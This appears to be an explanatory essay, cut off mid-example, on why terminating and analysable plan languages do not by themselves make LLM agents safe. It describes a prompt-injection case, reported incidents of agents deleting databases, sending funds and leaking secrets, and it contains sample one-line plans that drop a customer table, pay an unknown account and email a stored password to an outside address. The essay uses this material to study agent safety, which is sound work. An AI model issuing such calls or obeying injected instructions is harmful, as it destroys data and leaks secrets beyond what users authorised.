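# Why termination and analysability of an agent's plan do not make it safe

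## What do "terminating" and "analysable" mean for an agent's plan?

An AI agent is a system, usually a large language model with some software around it, that acts by calling tools. A tool is an ordinary function that might send an email, pay an account or delete a table from a database. The model names a tool and its arguments in text, and the software runs the function and returns the result to the model. Some effects of these calls are irreversible. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, gives the examples of a misconfigured deployment, an erroneous medication recommendation and an unauthorised payment.

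One proposal for making agents safer is to have the agent write its whole plan before it acts, as a short program in a deliberately limited language. Such a program is terminating, meaning it is certain to finish, and analysable, meaning software or a person can examine it before it runs. Both ideas come from the theory of programming languages and are much older than AI agents.

### Choosing each call, or planning first

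Many agents follow a pattern known as ReAct, in which the model starts from the user's request, picks one tool call, sees the result and then picks the next. This lets the agent adapt to surprises, but it also lets anything the model reads change what it does. Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* (2025) describes an email assistant with two tools, `fetch_mail` and `send_email`. The user asks for a summary of her mail. One message in the inbox claims that, for legal compliance, the assistant must send a summary to an outside address without mentioning it. The assistant obeys because current models cannot reliably tell instructions from data. This attack is called prompt injection.

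Alternatively, the agent can write the whole plan before it calls any tools. A plan here is a program that states which tools to call, in what order, with what arguments and under what conditions. Text that arrives later can fill in the plan's variables but cannot add steps to it.

In *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026) built an agent of this kind for websites and compared it with step-by-step agents. Their agent completed 77.8% of 581 web tasks, against 66.7% for a step-by-step agent that could also call the sites' programming interfaces. In a separate set of prompt-injection attacks, none succeeded against their agent, while 16.2% succeeded against that same step-by-step agent. Their agent was slower, at 327 seconds against 87. This seems to conflict with the argument in the guide *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) that step-by-step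 agents are slow on long tasks because they make one model call per action. The researchers also had to prepare a documented interface for each website by hand.

Some requests do not fit the method. Chow and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the agent to find an email from the boss and do whatever it says. No plan can exist until somebody has read the email. An earlier analysis, which they cite, found no such task in WebArena, the benchmark their tasks come from. Such requests are probably more common in offices, where "deal with my inbox" is a normal thing to ask.

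The plans in this experiment were written in ordinary Python, which has none of the restrictions discussed below. The injections failed because the model committed to its plan before it saw the attacker's text. Restricting the language is a further step that needs its own justification.

### An office assistant and its plan

Suppose a company runs an office assistant with five tools. `read_invoices` returns the unpaid invoices, oldest first. `read_secret` returns a stored password or key. `pay` moves money out of the company's account, `send_email` can email anyone, and `drop_table` deletes a database table and its contents. A plan's authority consists of the effects it can cause through its tools and permissions.

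An employee asks the assistant to pay the oldest invoice and tell the finance team. The agent writes three lines:

```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
send_email("finance", "Paid " + invoice.number)
```

The first line takes the first invoice on the list, the second pays it, and the third emails a confirmation. If the invoice is genuine and the company owes the money, running this plan harms nobody.

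### Terminating

The three-line plan has no loops, so each line runs at most once. It makes three tool calls and stops, provided that each tool returns an answer. A time limit on every call ensures this. The plan would still stop with an `if` added, since a branch can only skip lines.

To pay every invoice the agent needs a loop:

```
for invoice in read_invoices():
    pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
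    send_email("finance", "Paid " + invoice.number)
```

This is a bounded loop, meaning the number of rounds is fixed before the first begins. The software fetches the list once, and nothing inside the loop can lengthen it. With forty invoices, the plan makes 81 calls, one to read the list and two for each invoice. If a language allows only bounded loops and bans functions that call themselves, every program in it finishes on every input, which makes it a terminating language.

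An unbounded loop is different:

```
while read_invoices():
    invoice = read_invoices()[0]
    pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
send_email("finance", "All invoices paid")
```

This version runs as long as any unpaid invoice remains. Whether it stops depends on how soon a paid invoice leaves the list, which the text of the plan does not determine. If the accounting system updates its list overnight, the loop will pay the same invoice repeatedly until the list updates or the money runs out. A plan language that allowed only bounded loops would have prevented this, which is a point in its favour.

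Languages with unbounded loops, such as Python, are normally Turing-complete, meaning that they can express any computation a computer with unlimited memory could carry out. As a result, no algorithm can determine, for every program in such a language, whether it will finish. Turing-completeness is a property of a language, not of a single program, so the harmless three-line plan still terminates when the agent writes it in Python. If a plan is written in a terminating language, we know without inspecting it that it will finish.

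The programmer who blogs as matklad argues in *Primitive Recursive Functions For A Working Programmer* that knowing a program will terminate is worth very little, because bounded loops can still run for an absurdly long time. Repeating "add one" gives addition, repeating addition gives multiplication, repeating multiplication gives powers, and two more stages give a program that counts to 2 to the power of 2ⁿ. For n = 6 that is about 18 billion billion steps, or some 585 years at a billion steps a second. In practice, a program that needs centuries is no better than one that never stops. Any Turing-complete language also becomes terminating if the software that runs it counts steps and stops after, say, a billion.

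Both points also apply to agents, but an agent's actions can do harm before its plan halts. A plan to pay the first invoice one million times terminates. A step counter would eventually halt the `while` loop above, but only after some number of wrongful payments, and halting would not reverse them. The safety of a plan with tools depends on how many calls it can make and what they do, and termination alone limits neither.

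### Analysable

In *Static Program Analysis*, Møller and Schwartzbach define static analysis as the art of reasoning about what programs do without running them. A plan is analysable with respect to a question if we can answer that question by examining the plan's text. The same plan may be analysable for one question but not for another. The text of the three-line plan shows that it never calls `drop_table`, but not which account will receive the money, because that value will come from an invoice the assistant has not yet read.

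A useful checker for such questions is sound, meaning it never passes a plan that breaks the rule. The lecture slides *Program Analysis* contrast this with a complete analysis, which reports only real bugs and so raises no false alarms. For common programming languages, no automatic tool can be sound, complete and certain to finish on every interesting question about behaviour. Patrick Cousot explains in *Abstract Interpretation* that a designer has to give up one of the three. People who care about security usually give up completeness and accept false alarms.

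Take the rule that money may go only to accounts on the company's approved list. A sound check has to reject the three-line plan, since some invoice could carry an unapproved account number. Perhaps every invoice in the system is in fact fine, in which case the rejection is a false alarm. The agent can repair the plan with a branch:

```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
if invoice.account in approved_accounts:
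    pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
    send_email("finance", "Paid " + invoice.number)
```

Every path that reaches `pay` now goes through the test, so the check can pass the plan without knowing what the invoice will contain. Static analysis is attractive because one examination covers all the runs the plan could have, including those nobody thought to test.

A check is sound only with respect to a particular rule, and even a check that rejects every plan is sound. Bertrand Meyer writes in Communications of the ACM that false alarms do not cause catastrophes the way missed violations do, but that they are almost as bad in practice.

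The result also depends on assumptions about the tools. *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that checks an agent's plan before any tool runs. Each tool has a contract stating what it requires before a call and what it guarantees afterwards. For example, a payment tool may require a positive amount and a valid payment method, and guarantee that it returns a confirmation number. If a tool fails to meet its guarantee during a run, the system aborts, because the earlier verification no longer applies.

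Restricting a plan language helps a checker by removing constructs that hide where values come from. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a plan language with six kinds of step: fetching a stored result, calling a tool, having an isolated model process text, displaying something to the user, branching, and looping over a collection. The arguments of a call may refer to data but may not compute anything. The language has no arithmetic, text templates or user-defined functions, so it could not express the third line of the office plan, which joins "Paid " to an invoice number. These limits let a checker see from a plan's text which earlier values feed into each call.

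These bans go well beyond what termination requires, since arithmetic and text templates always finish. A plan that uses bounded loops to assemble an account number from characters scattered through an invoice will terminate, but a reader may be unable to work out whom it pays. Conversely, the runaway `while` loop might never end, but if the language can call tools only by name, a reader can see at a glance that the loop never calls `read_secret`. Neither guarantee implies the other, so an argument for one is not automatically an argument for both.

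### Two meanings of "safe"

In the theory of programs, "safety property" is a technical term. Informally it means that some stated bad thing never happens while the program runs. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, made the idea exact. They treat a run σ as an infinite sequence of states, repeating the last state forever if the program stops, and a property P as a set of runs. P is a safety property if

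∀σ: σ ∉ P ⇒ ∃i ≥ 0: ∀β: σᵢβ ∉ P

where σᵢ is the first i states of the run and β is any continuation. In words: if a run breaks the rule, there is an identifiable moment after which nothing that follows can put things right. "The plan never emails a value it got from `read_secret`" fits the definition. Once the email has gone, no later step makes the rule true again.

Their paper distinguishes liveness properties from safety properties. A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, and no finite part of a run can rule that out. Their examples include termination, which is one of the two guarantees that restricted plan languages offer. Termination is therefore not a safety property even in the technical sense. A plan can do anything and then stop, so termination excludes no bad event. A stated limit, such as "at most 81 tool calls", is a safety property, because a run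 breaks it at a definite moment, the 82nd call.

For a safety property in the technical sense, Alpern and Schneider require only that the bad thing be discrete, and they remark that good and bad things are not well-defined concepts. "The plan never sends email on a Tuesday" is as much a safety property as "the plan never deletes the payroll". A plan that does nothing satisfies every safety property in this sense, as Hillel Wayne observes in Computer Things' *Safety and Liveness Properties* (2020). Dantas and colleagues use the term more loosely for agents. They count any formula in a suitable logic about the sequence of actions as a safety property, which would include "a confirmation eventually goes out".

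In ordinary speech, a plan is safe if running it does no serious unwanted harm to anyone, including the supplier, the customers in the database and people who have never heard of the company. A plan can be safe in either the formal or the ordinary sense without being safe in the other. If a rule forbids emailing outsiders, a confirmation to a supplier is formally unsafe, though it hurts no one. The three-line plan obeys the rules about secrets and deleting tables even if a fraudster wrote the invoice. Girrens and Wang make the same observation about payments, where every step can be what the user asked for while the account number belongs to an attacker.

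People disagree about how far formal safety makes a plan safe in the ordinary sense. Designers want restricted plans because they can check them before any effect occurs and because, as Meijer argues, people can audit and understand an explicit workflow. Sceptics reply that harm comes from which calls a plan makes and with what values, and that a limited language barely constrains either. Others answer that restriction still helps, because restricted plans are simpler and reviewers catch more in them. Even matklad, writing about configuration files, allows that a ban on recursion and unbounded loops might nudge people towards simpler programs, but is unsure.

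## How can a plan that terminates and can be analysed still do harm?

The sceptics' point is easiest to test on very short plans, where the language has the least influence on the outcome.

### Three one-line plans

The office assistant could write any of the following. This plan deletes the company's customer records:

```
drop_table("customers")
```

This one pays a stranger, whose account number the agent might have picked up from a forged message:

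```
pay("account-7731", 9500)
```

And this one emails a stored password to somebody outside the company:

```
send_email("someone@elsewhere.example", read_secret("payroll"))
```

All three plans pass the usual tests. None contains a loop, so each finishes after one tool call, or two for the email. The arguments have the right types. `drop_table` receives a table name, `pay` receives an account and an amount, and `send_email` receives an address and a password, which is valid text. Each plan also names every tool it calls.

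A plan that pays a stranger is easier to analyse than a legitimate plan that pays the oldest invoice. The legitimate plan takes its account number from an invoice that hasn't been read yet, whereas the plan that pays a stranger has the number written in it. A checker could list everything the harmful plan will do before it runs.

A checker can establish with certainty that the first plan deletes the customer table. This protects the table only if somebody runs the check before the plan runs and has already decided that deleting the table is a reason to stop. Deleting it is sometimes the right plan, since a company that has moved its customers to a new system may want the old table gone. A simple rule would catch each of the three plans, but somebody has to write it.

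Meijer makes the same point in a talk written up in AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026). While he was preparing his slides, Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, blanked one of his source files with a single command. The write-up then defines a small language in which a plan can read a file, remove a file or finish with an answer. A plan that removes Meijer's file and then answers "Finished" is well formed. The checker rejects it only because the example also includes a rule under which no plan that removes a file can have a proof.

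That proof covers only deletion. According to the write-up, it does not show that the plan keeps data confidential. Even the guarantee against deletion fails if the interpreter, the software that carries out the plan, secretly deletes the files while handling a read. A step's effects depend on the tool it calls, and the plan's text contains only the tool's name.

### Computation and authority

All three plans get through because a restriction on a language limits computation, the working out of values from other values. The harm comes from the plan's authority, meaning its tools and permissions. When `drop_table("customers")` runs, the plan computes nothing. It passes a fixed word to a function, and the database deletes the table because the company gave the assistant permission to request it.

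A short argument shows how little a ban on loops takes away. Take any run in which an unrestricted agent, written in Python with every kind of loop, did harm. By the time of the harm it had made some finite number of calls, c₁, c₂, …, cₙ, each with particular arguments. Now write the plan

c₁; c₂; …; cₙ

with those arguments copied in as constants. This plan has no loops or branches, finishes after n calls and hides nothing. If the tools respond as they did before, it does the same harm. So if a language can call the same tools and write constants, banning loops puts no harmful sequence of calls out of reach.

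A short plan without loops cannot do everything a Python program can. Its writer must know the arguments to each call in advance, whereas a Python program can work them out as it runs, for instance by trying passwords until one works. A plan without loops would have to list every guess. A cap on the length of plans therefore has some value, since it rules out ten thousand small payments written line by line. But it does not rule out one large payment, and none of the plans above needs more than two calls.

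Python is Turing-complete, so a Python program may never stop. But if it runs with no tools, files or network connection, the most it can do by itself is waste processor time, which a time limit can stop. A one-line program that calls the payment tool can empty the company's account. A cautious company should prefer to run the Python program, even though only the payment program is guaranteed to terminate.

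Even an agent with almost no tools can do harm if people act on what it writes. Futurism's *Rogue AI Agent Triggers Emergency at Meta* describes an engineer who used an in-house agent to analyse a technical question that a colleague had posted on an internal forum. The agent posted its answer there without the engineer's approval. Another employee followed the advice, which was wrong, and for almost two hours engineers could see company and user data that they had no clearance for. Meta's spokesperson said that nobody mishandled user data, and pointed out that the agent had only provided a response. But that response took effect through the permissions of the employee who followed it. An assessment of an agent's authority should therefore include what people are likely to do on its advice.

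### Why people value languages that are not Turing-complete

The same confusion has arisen over configuration languages, which people use to write a program's settings. Their designers often advertise that the languages are not Turing-complete. Gabriella Gonzalez, who created one such language, Dhall, argued in 2020 that this property guarantees little by itself but is a sign of other good design choices.

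In the 2024 post, matklad is more critical of the label "not Turing-complete", arguing that nobody wants a lack of Turing-completeness for its own sake. People want a language to be deterministic, so that the same file always gives the same result, and to have an exact definition that every implementation follows. They also want it to be pure, meaning that the result does not depend on files or settings elsewhere on the machine, and to keep secrets away from an attacker. These properties are largely independent of Turing-completeness, but they have no catchy collective name, so "not Turing-complete" serves as "a sort of rallying cry" for them.

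The post also proves that the restriction barely limits computation. Any program that finishes within 2 to the power of 2ⁿ steps, where n is the size of its input, can be rewritten using only bounded loops. The proof encodes the computer's whole state, including its memory, as a single number. Each step of the computer becomes arithmetic on that number, and a bounded loop repeats the step as many times as the limit allows. Nearly every practical program finishes far sooner than the limit, so a terminating language with arithmetic can compute almost anything people compute in Python, though the code may be roundabout and extremely slow.

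Gonzalez and matklad agree that the missing power contributes little, and disagree mostly on whether the label is useful shorthand or confusing. The post's more important point for agents is that security comes from denying the language general input and output, so that a configuration file cannot open other files or contact the network. The main remaining attack is then to waste the processor's time.

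Restricted configuration languages are secure because they have no input or output. A plan language cannot do without these entirely, because a plan exists in order to act. Its designers may start with a language that has neither, but they then have to add tools, and each tool restores some input or output. The good record of restricted configuration languages is therefore weak evidence that restricted plans are safe. Plan languages can still share their determinism and exact definition. Given the same tool responses, a plan in such a language makes the same calls each time, which makes it easier to predict. But a plan that deletes a customer table with `drop_table("customers")` is just as predictable.

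### Verified programs in the Linux kernel

Linux's eBPF system is a test case from outside AI. It lets suitably privileged users load small programs into the kernel, the core of the operating system, where an ordinary mistake could crash the machine. Before Linux loads a program, a verifier checks the code and accepts it only if it can establish that the program will finish and will touch only the memory it may use. Designers of agent plans want the same two guarantees, and engineers rely on them on production servers.

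An eBPF program that passes the Linux verifier may still discard every packet that reaches the machine's network card. Discarding packets is a normal use of eBPF, since firewalls need to do it. The verifier does not check whether anyone wanted those packets, so a program with a badly chosen filter can cut a server off from its users even if it stays within its memory and finishes on time. Linux deals with this risk by restricting who may load programs and which kernel functions each type of program may call.

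### Harm through a few ordinary calls

In the cases below, agents deleted data, moved money or exposed secrets. The cases show how much harm one or two calls can do, and what permission each call relied on. They do not show how often restricted plans go wrong, because the agents chose their actions as they went along and none of them first wrote a plan in a restricted language.

In April 2026 a coding agent deleted the live database of PocketOS, whose software car-rental firms use for reservations and payments. PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, described the incident in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, written while the data was still missing. The agent was Cursor, a code editor, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. During routine work in staging, a copy of the system for testing, it found a credential that did not match. It tried to fix this by deleting a volume, a unit of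 storage at the hosting company Railway, using an access token from a file unrelated to the task. Crane had created that token for adding and removing web domains.

The deletion took one request. *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab's account of the incident for Railway, shows that the request was a single `volumeDelete` operation with the volume's identifier as its only argument. Crane says it took nine seconds. The token gave access to everything in the account, the widest access Railway offers. Abdelwahab says that narrower tokens existed, but concedes that the process for creating a token did not make the right choice obvious. Crane says that nobody could restrict a token's access at all. Either way, a token intended for domain names could delete a live database.

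The newest backup that Crane could restore was three months old. The next morning, the rental firms had no record of the customers who arrived to collect cars. Crane spent the day helping the firms rebuild bookings from payment histories and emails. Railway later recovered the data, according to Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database*, so the loss was limited to a few days of disruption and emergency work.

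A reviewer who saw the `volumeDelete` request beforehand would have known that a volume would be deleted, but could not have told from the identifier whether it held test data or the live business's data. When Crane asked the agent for an explanation, it wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. A model's explanation after the event is poor evidence of why it acted, but people also make wrong guesses of this kind, and banning loops would not prevent them.

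A similar deletion happened to Jason Lemkin, founder of the software community SaaStr, in July 2025, while he was building an application with a coding agent from the company Replit. According to Fortune (2025), the agent wiped a live database with records on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. Lemkin had declared a freeze on all changes, but the freeze did not remove the agent's access. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, wrote that an agent working in development had deleted production data and that this "should never be possible". Replit then began automatically separating development and production databases.

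Lemkin lost little data. The agent told him that a rollback, which returns an application to an earlier state, would not work. He believed the agent and nearly did not try the rollback, but when he did, he recovered the records. Replit's introductory guide had described a rollback that covers database changes, as The Stack (2025) pointed out.

The payment case is harder to reverse. In February 2026 Nik Pash, an OpenAI employee, gave a trading agent called Lobstar Wilde a cryptocurrency wallet with $50,000 in it and the goal of making a million. He also told it to make no mistakes, according to SolanaFloor. A stranger on X asked the agent for 4 SOL, units of the cryptocurrency Solana, for his uncle's tetanus treatment. The agent sent him its entire holding of its own memecoin, a novelty cryptocurrency, worth roughly $441,000. The OECD incident monitor's entry, *AI Trading Bot Accidentally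 Transfers Entire Crypto Holdings Due to Misinterpretation* (2026), attributes the transfer to a misreading of the request and notes that nobody can reverse a blockchain transfer. In the terms of the office example, the transfer was one call to `pay` with a valid recipient and a valid number, and the instruction to make no mistakes did not limit the agent's authority to make that call.

Even a call that only reads a file can leak secrets. TechRadar's *I leaked secrets* reports an incident that the security vendor NordLayer found at a company. An engineer asked a coding assistant to examine some proposed changes, and the project's instructions pointed it to an access token in a settings file. The same file held production passwords and the keys to the company's personnel system. In ten sessions over three weeks, the assistant read the whole file and sent its contents to the outside AI service.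 Later, in a copy of the project that lacked the file, the assistant retrieved all the computer's environment variables, which are settings that programs share, and exposed more passwords. The article reports no misuse of the passwords and keys, but a company in this position should replace them all.

The only permission involved was permission to read. When a step-by-step agent reads something, the result goes back to the model, so if another company runs that model, reading alone sends the data outside. Many people would still class reading a file as harmless and worry about deleting and paying instead. An agent that plans first may avoid sending the data outside, because the values can stay in the plan's variables without going back to the model. That benefit would come from planning first, so a plan in ordinary Python would have it too.

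A closer match for the password email is a weakly supported report of an agent sending confidential information to an outsider. In Deccan Herald's *AI Business Secrets*, Sridhar Vembu, the founder of the software company Zoho, describes an email in which a startup founder offered his company for sale and disclosed a rival bidder's name and price. A second email, supposedly from the founder's "browser AI agent", apologised for the disclosure. The story rests on Vembu's post, and some readers suspected that a human was using the AI as an excuse in a negotiating trick.

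Individual cases cannot show how common such harm is. Cyera, a data-security company, looked at 7,246 public reports of incidents from September 2023 to May 2026. *ИИ-агенты навредили компаниям в 188 случаях без взлома*, an article in the Russian outlet RIAMO, gives some of the figures. Of these reports, 344 concerned companies, and Cyera found real damage in 137. Data deletion accounted for 65 of the 137. The agent almost always had access to a command line or a code repository and did not ask anyone to confirm dangerous commands. Cyera sells products in this area, and public reports are a biased sample. Companies notice a missing database within minutes but may never notice a leaked password, so the share of leaks is probably higher than these figures suggest. Still, the pattern of wide access and no confirmation matches the cases above.

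### Reducing authority

If harm comes from authority, the obvious remedy is to give the agent less of it. Paying invoices requires only three of the assistant's five tools, and the other two are `drop_table` and `read_secret`. Without those two, the assistant cannot write a working version of the deletion plan or the password email in any language, unless it can reach the data another way.

The payment tool has to stay, but its arguments can be narrower. Suppose the company replaces `pay`, which accepts any account and any amount, with `pay_invoice`, which accepts only an invoice number. The new tool looks up the account and the amount in the company's approved supplier records and refuses to pay an invoice twice. A second tool, `notify_finance`, replaces `send_email` and can write only to the finance team. The honest plan becomes:

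```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
pay_invoice(invoice.number)
notify_finance("Paid " + invoice.number)
```

If payments can go only to suppliers on an approved list, the invoice-paying plan works as before, but a plan to pay a stranger can't be written because there is no field for the account number. The invoice-paying plan would still pay a fraudulent invoice from an approved supplier.

The narrower tool also limits the harm an endless loop can do. The `while` loop that kept paying the same invoice until the accounting system caught up would now pay it once, and the tool would refuse every further attempt until somebody stopped the loop. The company can therefore tolerate a program that may not terminate, as long as it uses the narrow tool. The original tool lets even a one-line plan that always terminates empty the account.

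Where an agent must have a dangerous tool, the company can make the tool's effects reversible. Railway's dashboard already kept deleted volumes for 48 hours, but the interface that the PocketOS agent called destroyed them immediately. Within days of the incident, Railway's *Undoable volume deletes* (2026) announced that the interface would also wait 48 hours, so that an "overeager agent" could not erase data with one request. The customer could then undo the same one-line request, even though the agent's language and reasoning had not changed.

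A grace period helps only if somebody notices the problem in time. The PocketOS deletion happened on a Friday afternoon, so the 48 hours would have run out on Sunday afternoon, when few small companies check their storage. Some harms are also harder to reverse than others. A bank can hold a payment for a day before sending it, but once a password has leaked, the company can only change it. Most of the protection for secrets therefore has to come from keeping them out of the agent's reach.

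It is hard to keep things out of an agent's reach, because its authority includes every password and token it can find, whatever its list of tools contains. TechRadar describes a second incident, at a company whose official connection kept its AI assistant away from some internal documents. An employee asked the assistant whether an access token might offer another way in, and it did. The PocketOS agent likewise used a token that nobody had meant to give it. A tool that runs arbitrary commands on a computer gives the agent the authority of everything on that computer, so a plan language that includes such a tool is not really restricted. Railway's answer is an interface with short-lived access and a fixed set of tools. Abdelwahab's claim that this makes it impossible for an agent to go rogue is too strong, because an agent can still misuse those tools, but the damage is limited to what they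 can do.

Each tool that a company removes leaves the agent able to do fewer jobs, and people want agents largely because they can do many. An assistant that can only pay approved invoices and write to finance is little more than ordinary accounting software. Companies will therefore keep giving agents more authority than is strictly safe, and will want other protections.

Restricted plan languages do limit what a plan can do, as their defenders can fairly point out. An ordinary Python program can load a library, open a file or build new code while it runs, so its list of tools does not cover everything it can do unless a sandbox, software that walls the program off, blocks those other actions. A restricted language cannot express them, so a reader can treat the list of tools as complete. This improves safety, but the improvement comes from leaving out libraries, files and code built at run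 time, and a language could leave those out and still allow unbounded loops. The benefit also depends on which tools are listed. If `drop_table` is on the list, the reader knows only that any plan might delete the customer records, and has to check each plan to find out whether it does.

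## Which questions about a plan does a restricted language make decidable?

To check a plan that may use `pay`, a reviewer has to answer a question such as "is there any input on which this plan calls `pay`?" The input is everything the plan receives, including the user's data and the results that tools return. The question is easy if the plan never mentions `pay` or calls it on the first line. It is harder when the call depends on a condition, because the reviewer must then work out whether the condition can ever hold.

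A question is decidable for a language if some algorithm answers it correctly, in finite time, for every program in the language. Guaranteeing that every plan finishes is not enough to make the question about `pay` decidable, and neither is banning all loops if the language keeps multiplication.

### Unbounded loops

In Python, an agent could write this plan:

```
simulate(M, w)
pay("account-7731", 9500)
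```

`simulate` runs some computing machine M on some data w until M stops, which requires a `while` loop. The plan reaches `pay` on its second line only if M stops. An algorithm that could answer the question about `pay` for every Python plan could also determine, for every M and w, whether M stops on w. This is the halting problem, which no algorithm can solve.

matklad gives the usual proof. Suppose somebody had a function `halts` that always predicted correctly whether a program stops on a given input. Write a new program that reads the text of any program, uses `halts` to predict whether that program stops on its own text, and then does the opposite, looping forever if the prediction is "stops" and stopping otherwise. Now run the new program on its own text. If the prediction is that it stops, it loops forever, and if the prediction is that it loops, it stops. The prediction is wrong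 either way, so `halts` cannot exist.

Rice's theorem, from 1953, extends this to every property of a program's behaviour that some programs have and others lack. No algorithm can decide, for every program in a Turing-complete language, whether the program has such a property. The theorem does not cover properties of the program's text, such as whether it is shorter than four kilobytes, which is easy to check.

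The theorem rules out a single method that is right about all programs, but it doesn't prevent anyone from settling a particular case. People often forget this limit, though *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines* (2024) includes it right after the statement of the theorem. A reviewer can see that a ten-line Python plan never makes a payment. A checker can also be right every time it answers "yes" or "no", if it is allowed to answer "don't know" in other cases.

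### Bounded loops

Now ban unbounded loops and recursion, so that every plan finishes. The agent can still write this:

```
state = start(M, w)
for i in range(n):
    state = step(M, state)
if halted(state):
    pay("account-7731", 9500)
```

The number n is an input, perhaps one that the user types in. The loop runs exactly n rounds, each carrying out one step of M, and then the plan ends. If M stops after 4,000 steps, the plan calls `pay` whenever n is at least 4,000. If M never stops, the plan doesn't call `pay` for any value of n. So "is there an input on which this plan calls `pay`?" has the same answer as "does M stop?" and is therefore still undecidable, even though every run of every plan finishes.

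Requiring the plan to run quickly doesn't make the question easier either. If the loop took one step of M for each invoice in a list, the plan's running time would grow only in proportion to the length of the list, but the question would be just as hard.

Restricting programs to bounded loops does not make it decidable whether they ever return zero. Such programs compute the primitive recursive functions. In *Primitive recursive functions versus partial recursive functions*, Matos (2016) found that this question is exactly as undecidable for them as it is for functions that unrestricted programs compute.

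Some other questions get easier. To find out whether a terminating plan makes a payment on a given input, a checker can run it on that input with harmless stand-ins for the tools. A Python plan might hang, so the same test may give no answer. Whether two plans behave alike on every input remains undecidable, but Matos classes the question as less undecidable for terminating programs. If two terminating plans differ on some input, a search through the inputs will eventually find the difference, but this isn't guaranteed if either plan may hang.

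Rice's theorem does not hold for terminating languages, because "this plan pays when n is 5" is a property of behaviour and an algorithm can decide it. In *A Rice-like theorem for primitive recursive functions*, Hoyrup (2015) worked out exactly which properties of behaviour are decidable instead. His result covers any class of always-terminating programs that an algorithm can list, including polynomial-time programs. He returned to the subject in *The Decidable Properties of Subrecursive Functions* (2016).

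Suppose one person has the text of such a program, and another has only an upper limit on its size and a box that returns its output on any input. Surprisingly, Hoyrup proved in 2015 that the second person can confirm any property of what the program computes that the first person's algorithm can confirm. Only finitely many programs fit within the size limit, so the second person can run them all alongside the box and discard each one whose output differs. Meanwhile, he applies the first person's algorithm to every program on the list. Once it has confirmed the property for all those not yet discarded, the program in the box must have it.

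The theorem doesn't account for how much computation is needed, and nobody could really run every program of a given size. A human reader can also learn a lot from a program's text, and the theorem covers only questions about what a program computes. Still, it weakens the idea that a plan's behaviour is easy to work out if the plan terminates.

The undecidability also limits what testing can establish. If there were a formula B(k) such that any plan of length k that ever pays does so for some input no larger than B(k), a checker could settle the question by trying every input up to B(k). Since the question is undecidable, no such formula exists. For any limit that an algorithm could calculate from a plan's length, some fairly short plan pays only on inputs beyond that limit.

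### Multiplication without loops

A language with no loops at all looks much safer. But suppose it allows whole numbers of any size, multiplication and a branch on whether two values are equal:

```
if x*x*x + y*y*y + z*z*z == 42:
    pay("account-7731", 9500)
```

This plan has one condition and one call. For a long time nobody knew whether any integers x, y and z would trigger the payment. In 2019 Andrew Booker and Andrew Sutherland found three that do, each seventeen digits long.

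In 1900 David Hilbert asked for a general method to determine whether a given polynomial with whole-number coefficients equals zero for some choice of whole numbers. In 1970 Yuri Matiyasevich, building on work by Martin Davis, Hilary Putnam and Julia Robinson, completed a proof that no such method exists. An algorithm that decided the question about `pay` for every plan in this language would be such a method, because any of Hilbert's polynomials could be put in a plan's condition. The question about `pay` is therefore undecidable, even for plans that consist of a single `if` and a single call.

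Real computers hold only numbers of limited size, so a plan has finitely many possible inputs. If the plan always terminates, a checker can run it on all of them, which makes the question decidable, as Matos also observes. The same approach fails for a Python plan with unlimited memory, which may hang on the first input. But even for a terminating plan, three 64-bit inputs have 2 to the power of 192 combinations, or about 6 followed by 57 zeros, so checking them all is possible only in principle.

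Some ordinary tasks need multiplication, such as comparing an invoice's total with quantity times unit price. The conditions in these tasks will nearly always be far simpler than a sum of three cubes, and a checker will usually be able to decide them. The theorem only rules out a guarantee that it always will.

### Finite values and linear arithmetic

The question becomes decidable when a plan has no loops and the language also limits what it can do with its data. One such limit is to allow each input only finitely many values, such as yes or no, or one of a fixed list of departments. A plan with ten yes-or-no inputs has 1,024 combinations, and a checker can try them all.

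Another way is to allow numbers of any size but only linear arithmetic, meaning addition, subtraction and multiplication by constants. Consider this plan:

```
if amount + fee <= 500 and amount - 2*fee >= 450 and fee >= 20:
    pay(invoice.account, amount)
```

The first condition requires the amount to be at most 500 − fee, and the second requires it to be at least 450 + 2 × fee. Both can hold only if 450 + 2 × fee ≤ 500 − fee, so the fee can be at most 16⅔. The third condition requires a fee of at least 20, so the plan never pays. A checker can do this mechanically by removing one variable at a time until it reaches either a contradiction or a range of possible values. A plan without loops has only finitely many routes through its branches, so the checker can collect the conditions along each route and test them this way.

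The method is exact for fractions. For whole numbers it also needs divisibility tests, because 2x = 2y + 1 has solutions in fractions but none in whole numbers. Mojżesz Presburger showed in 1929 that these tests are enough. The method would not work if two inputs were multiplied, because the conditions would no longer be linear and finding the limit on one variable would require dividing by another.

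Decidable does not mean quick. Take a plan whose inputs are all true or false:

```
if (a or b) and (not a or c) and (not b or not c):
    pay("account-7731", 9500)
```

Deciding whether any input makes this plan call `pay` is a small case of the satisfiability problem, which asks whether a logical formula can be true. The plan's condition can be any such formula, so the question is NP-hard, meaning it is at least as hard as many scheduling, routing and puzzle problems for which no known method avoids explosive growth in running time in the worst case. Sixty true-or-false inputs have over a billion billion combinations. This rarely matters in practice for short plans, because an office plan would have only a handful of variables and modern satisfiability solvers handle industrial formulas with many thousands.

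A loop need not spoil decidability if the plan remembers little. This plan goes once through the invoices and keeps a single true-or-false value:

```
seen_urgent = False
for invoice in read_invoices():
    if seen_urgent and not invoice.approved:
        pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
    if invoice.urgent:
        seen_urgent = True
```

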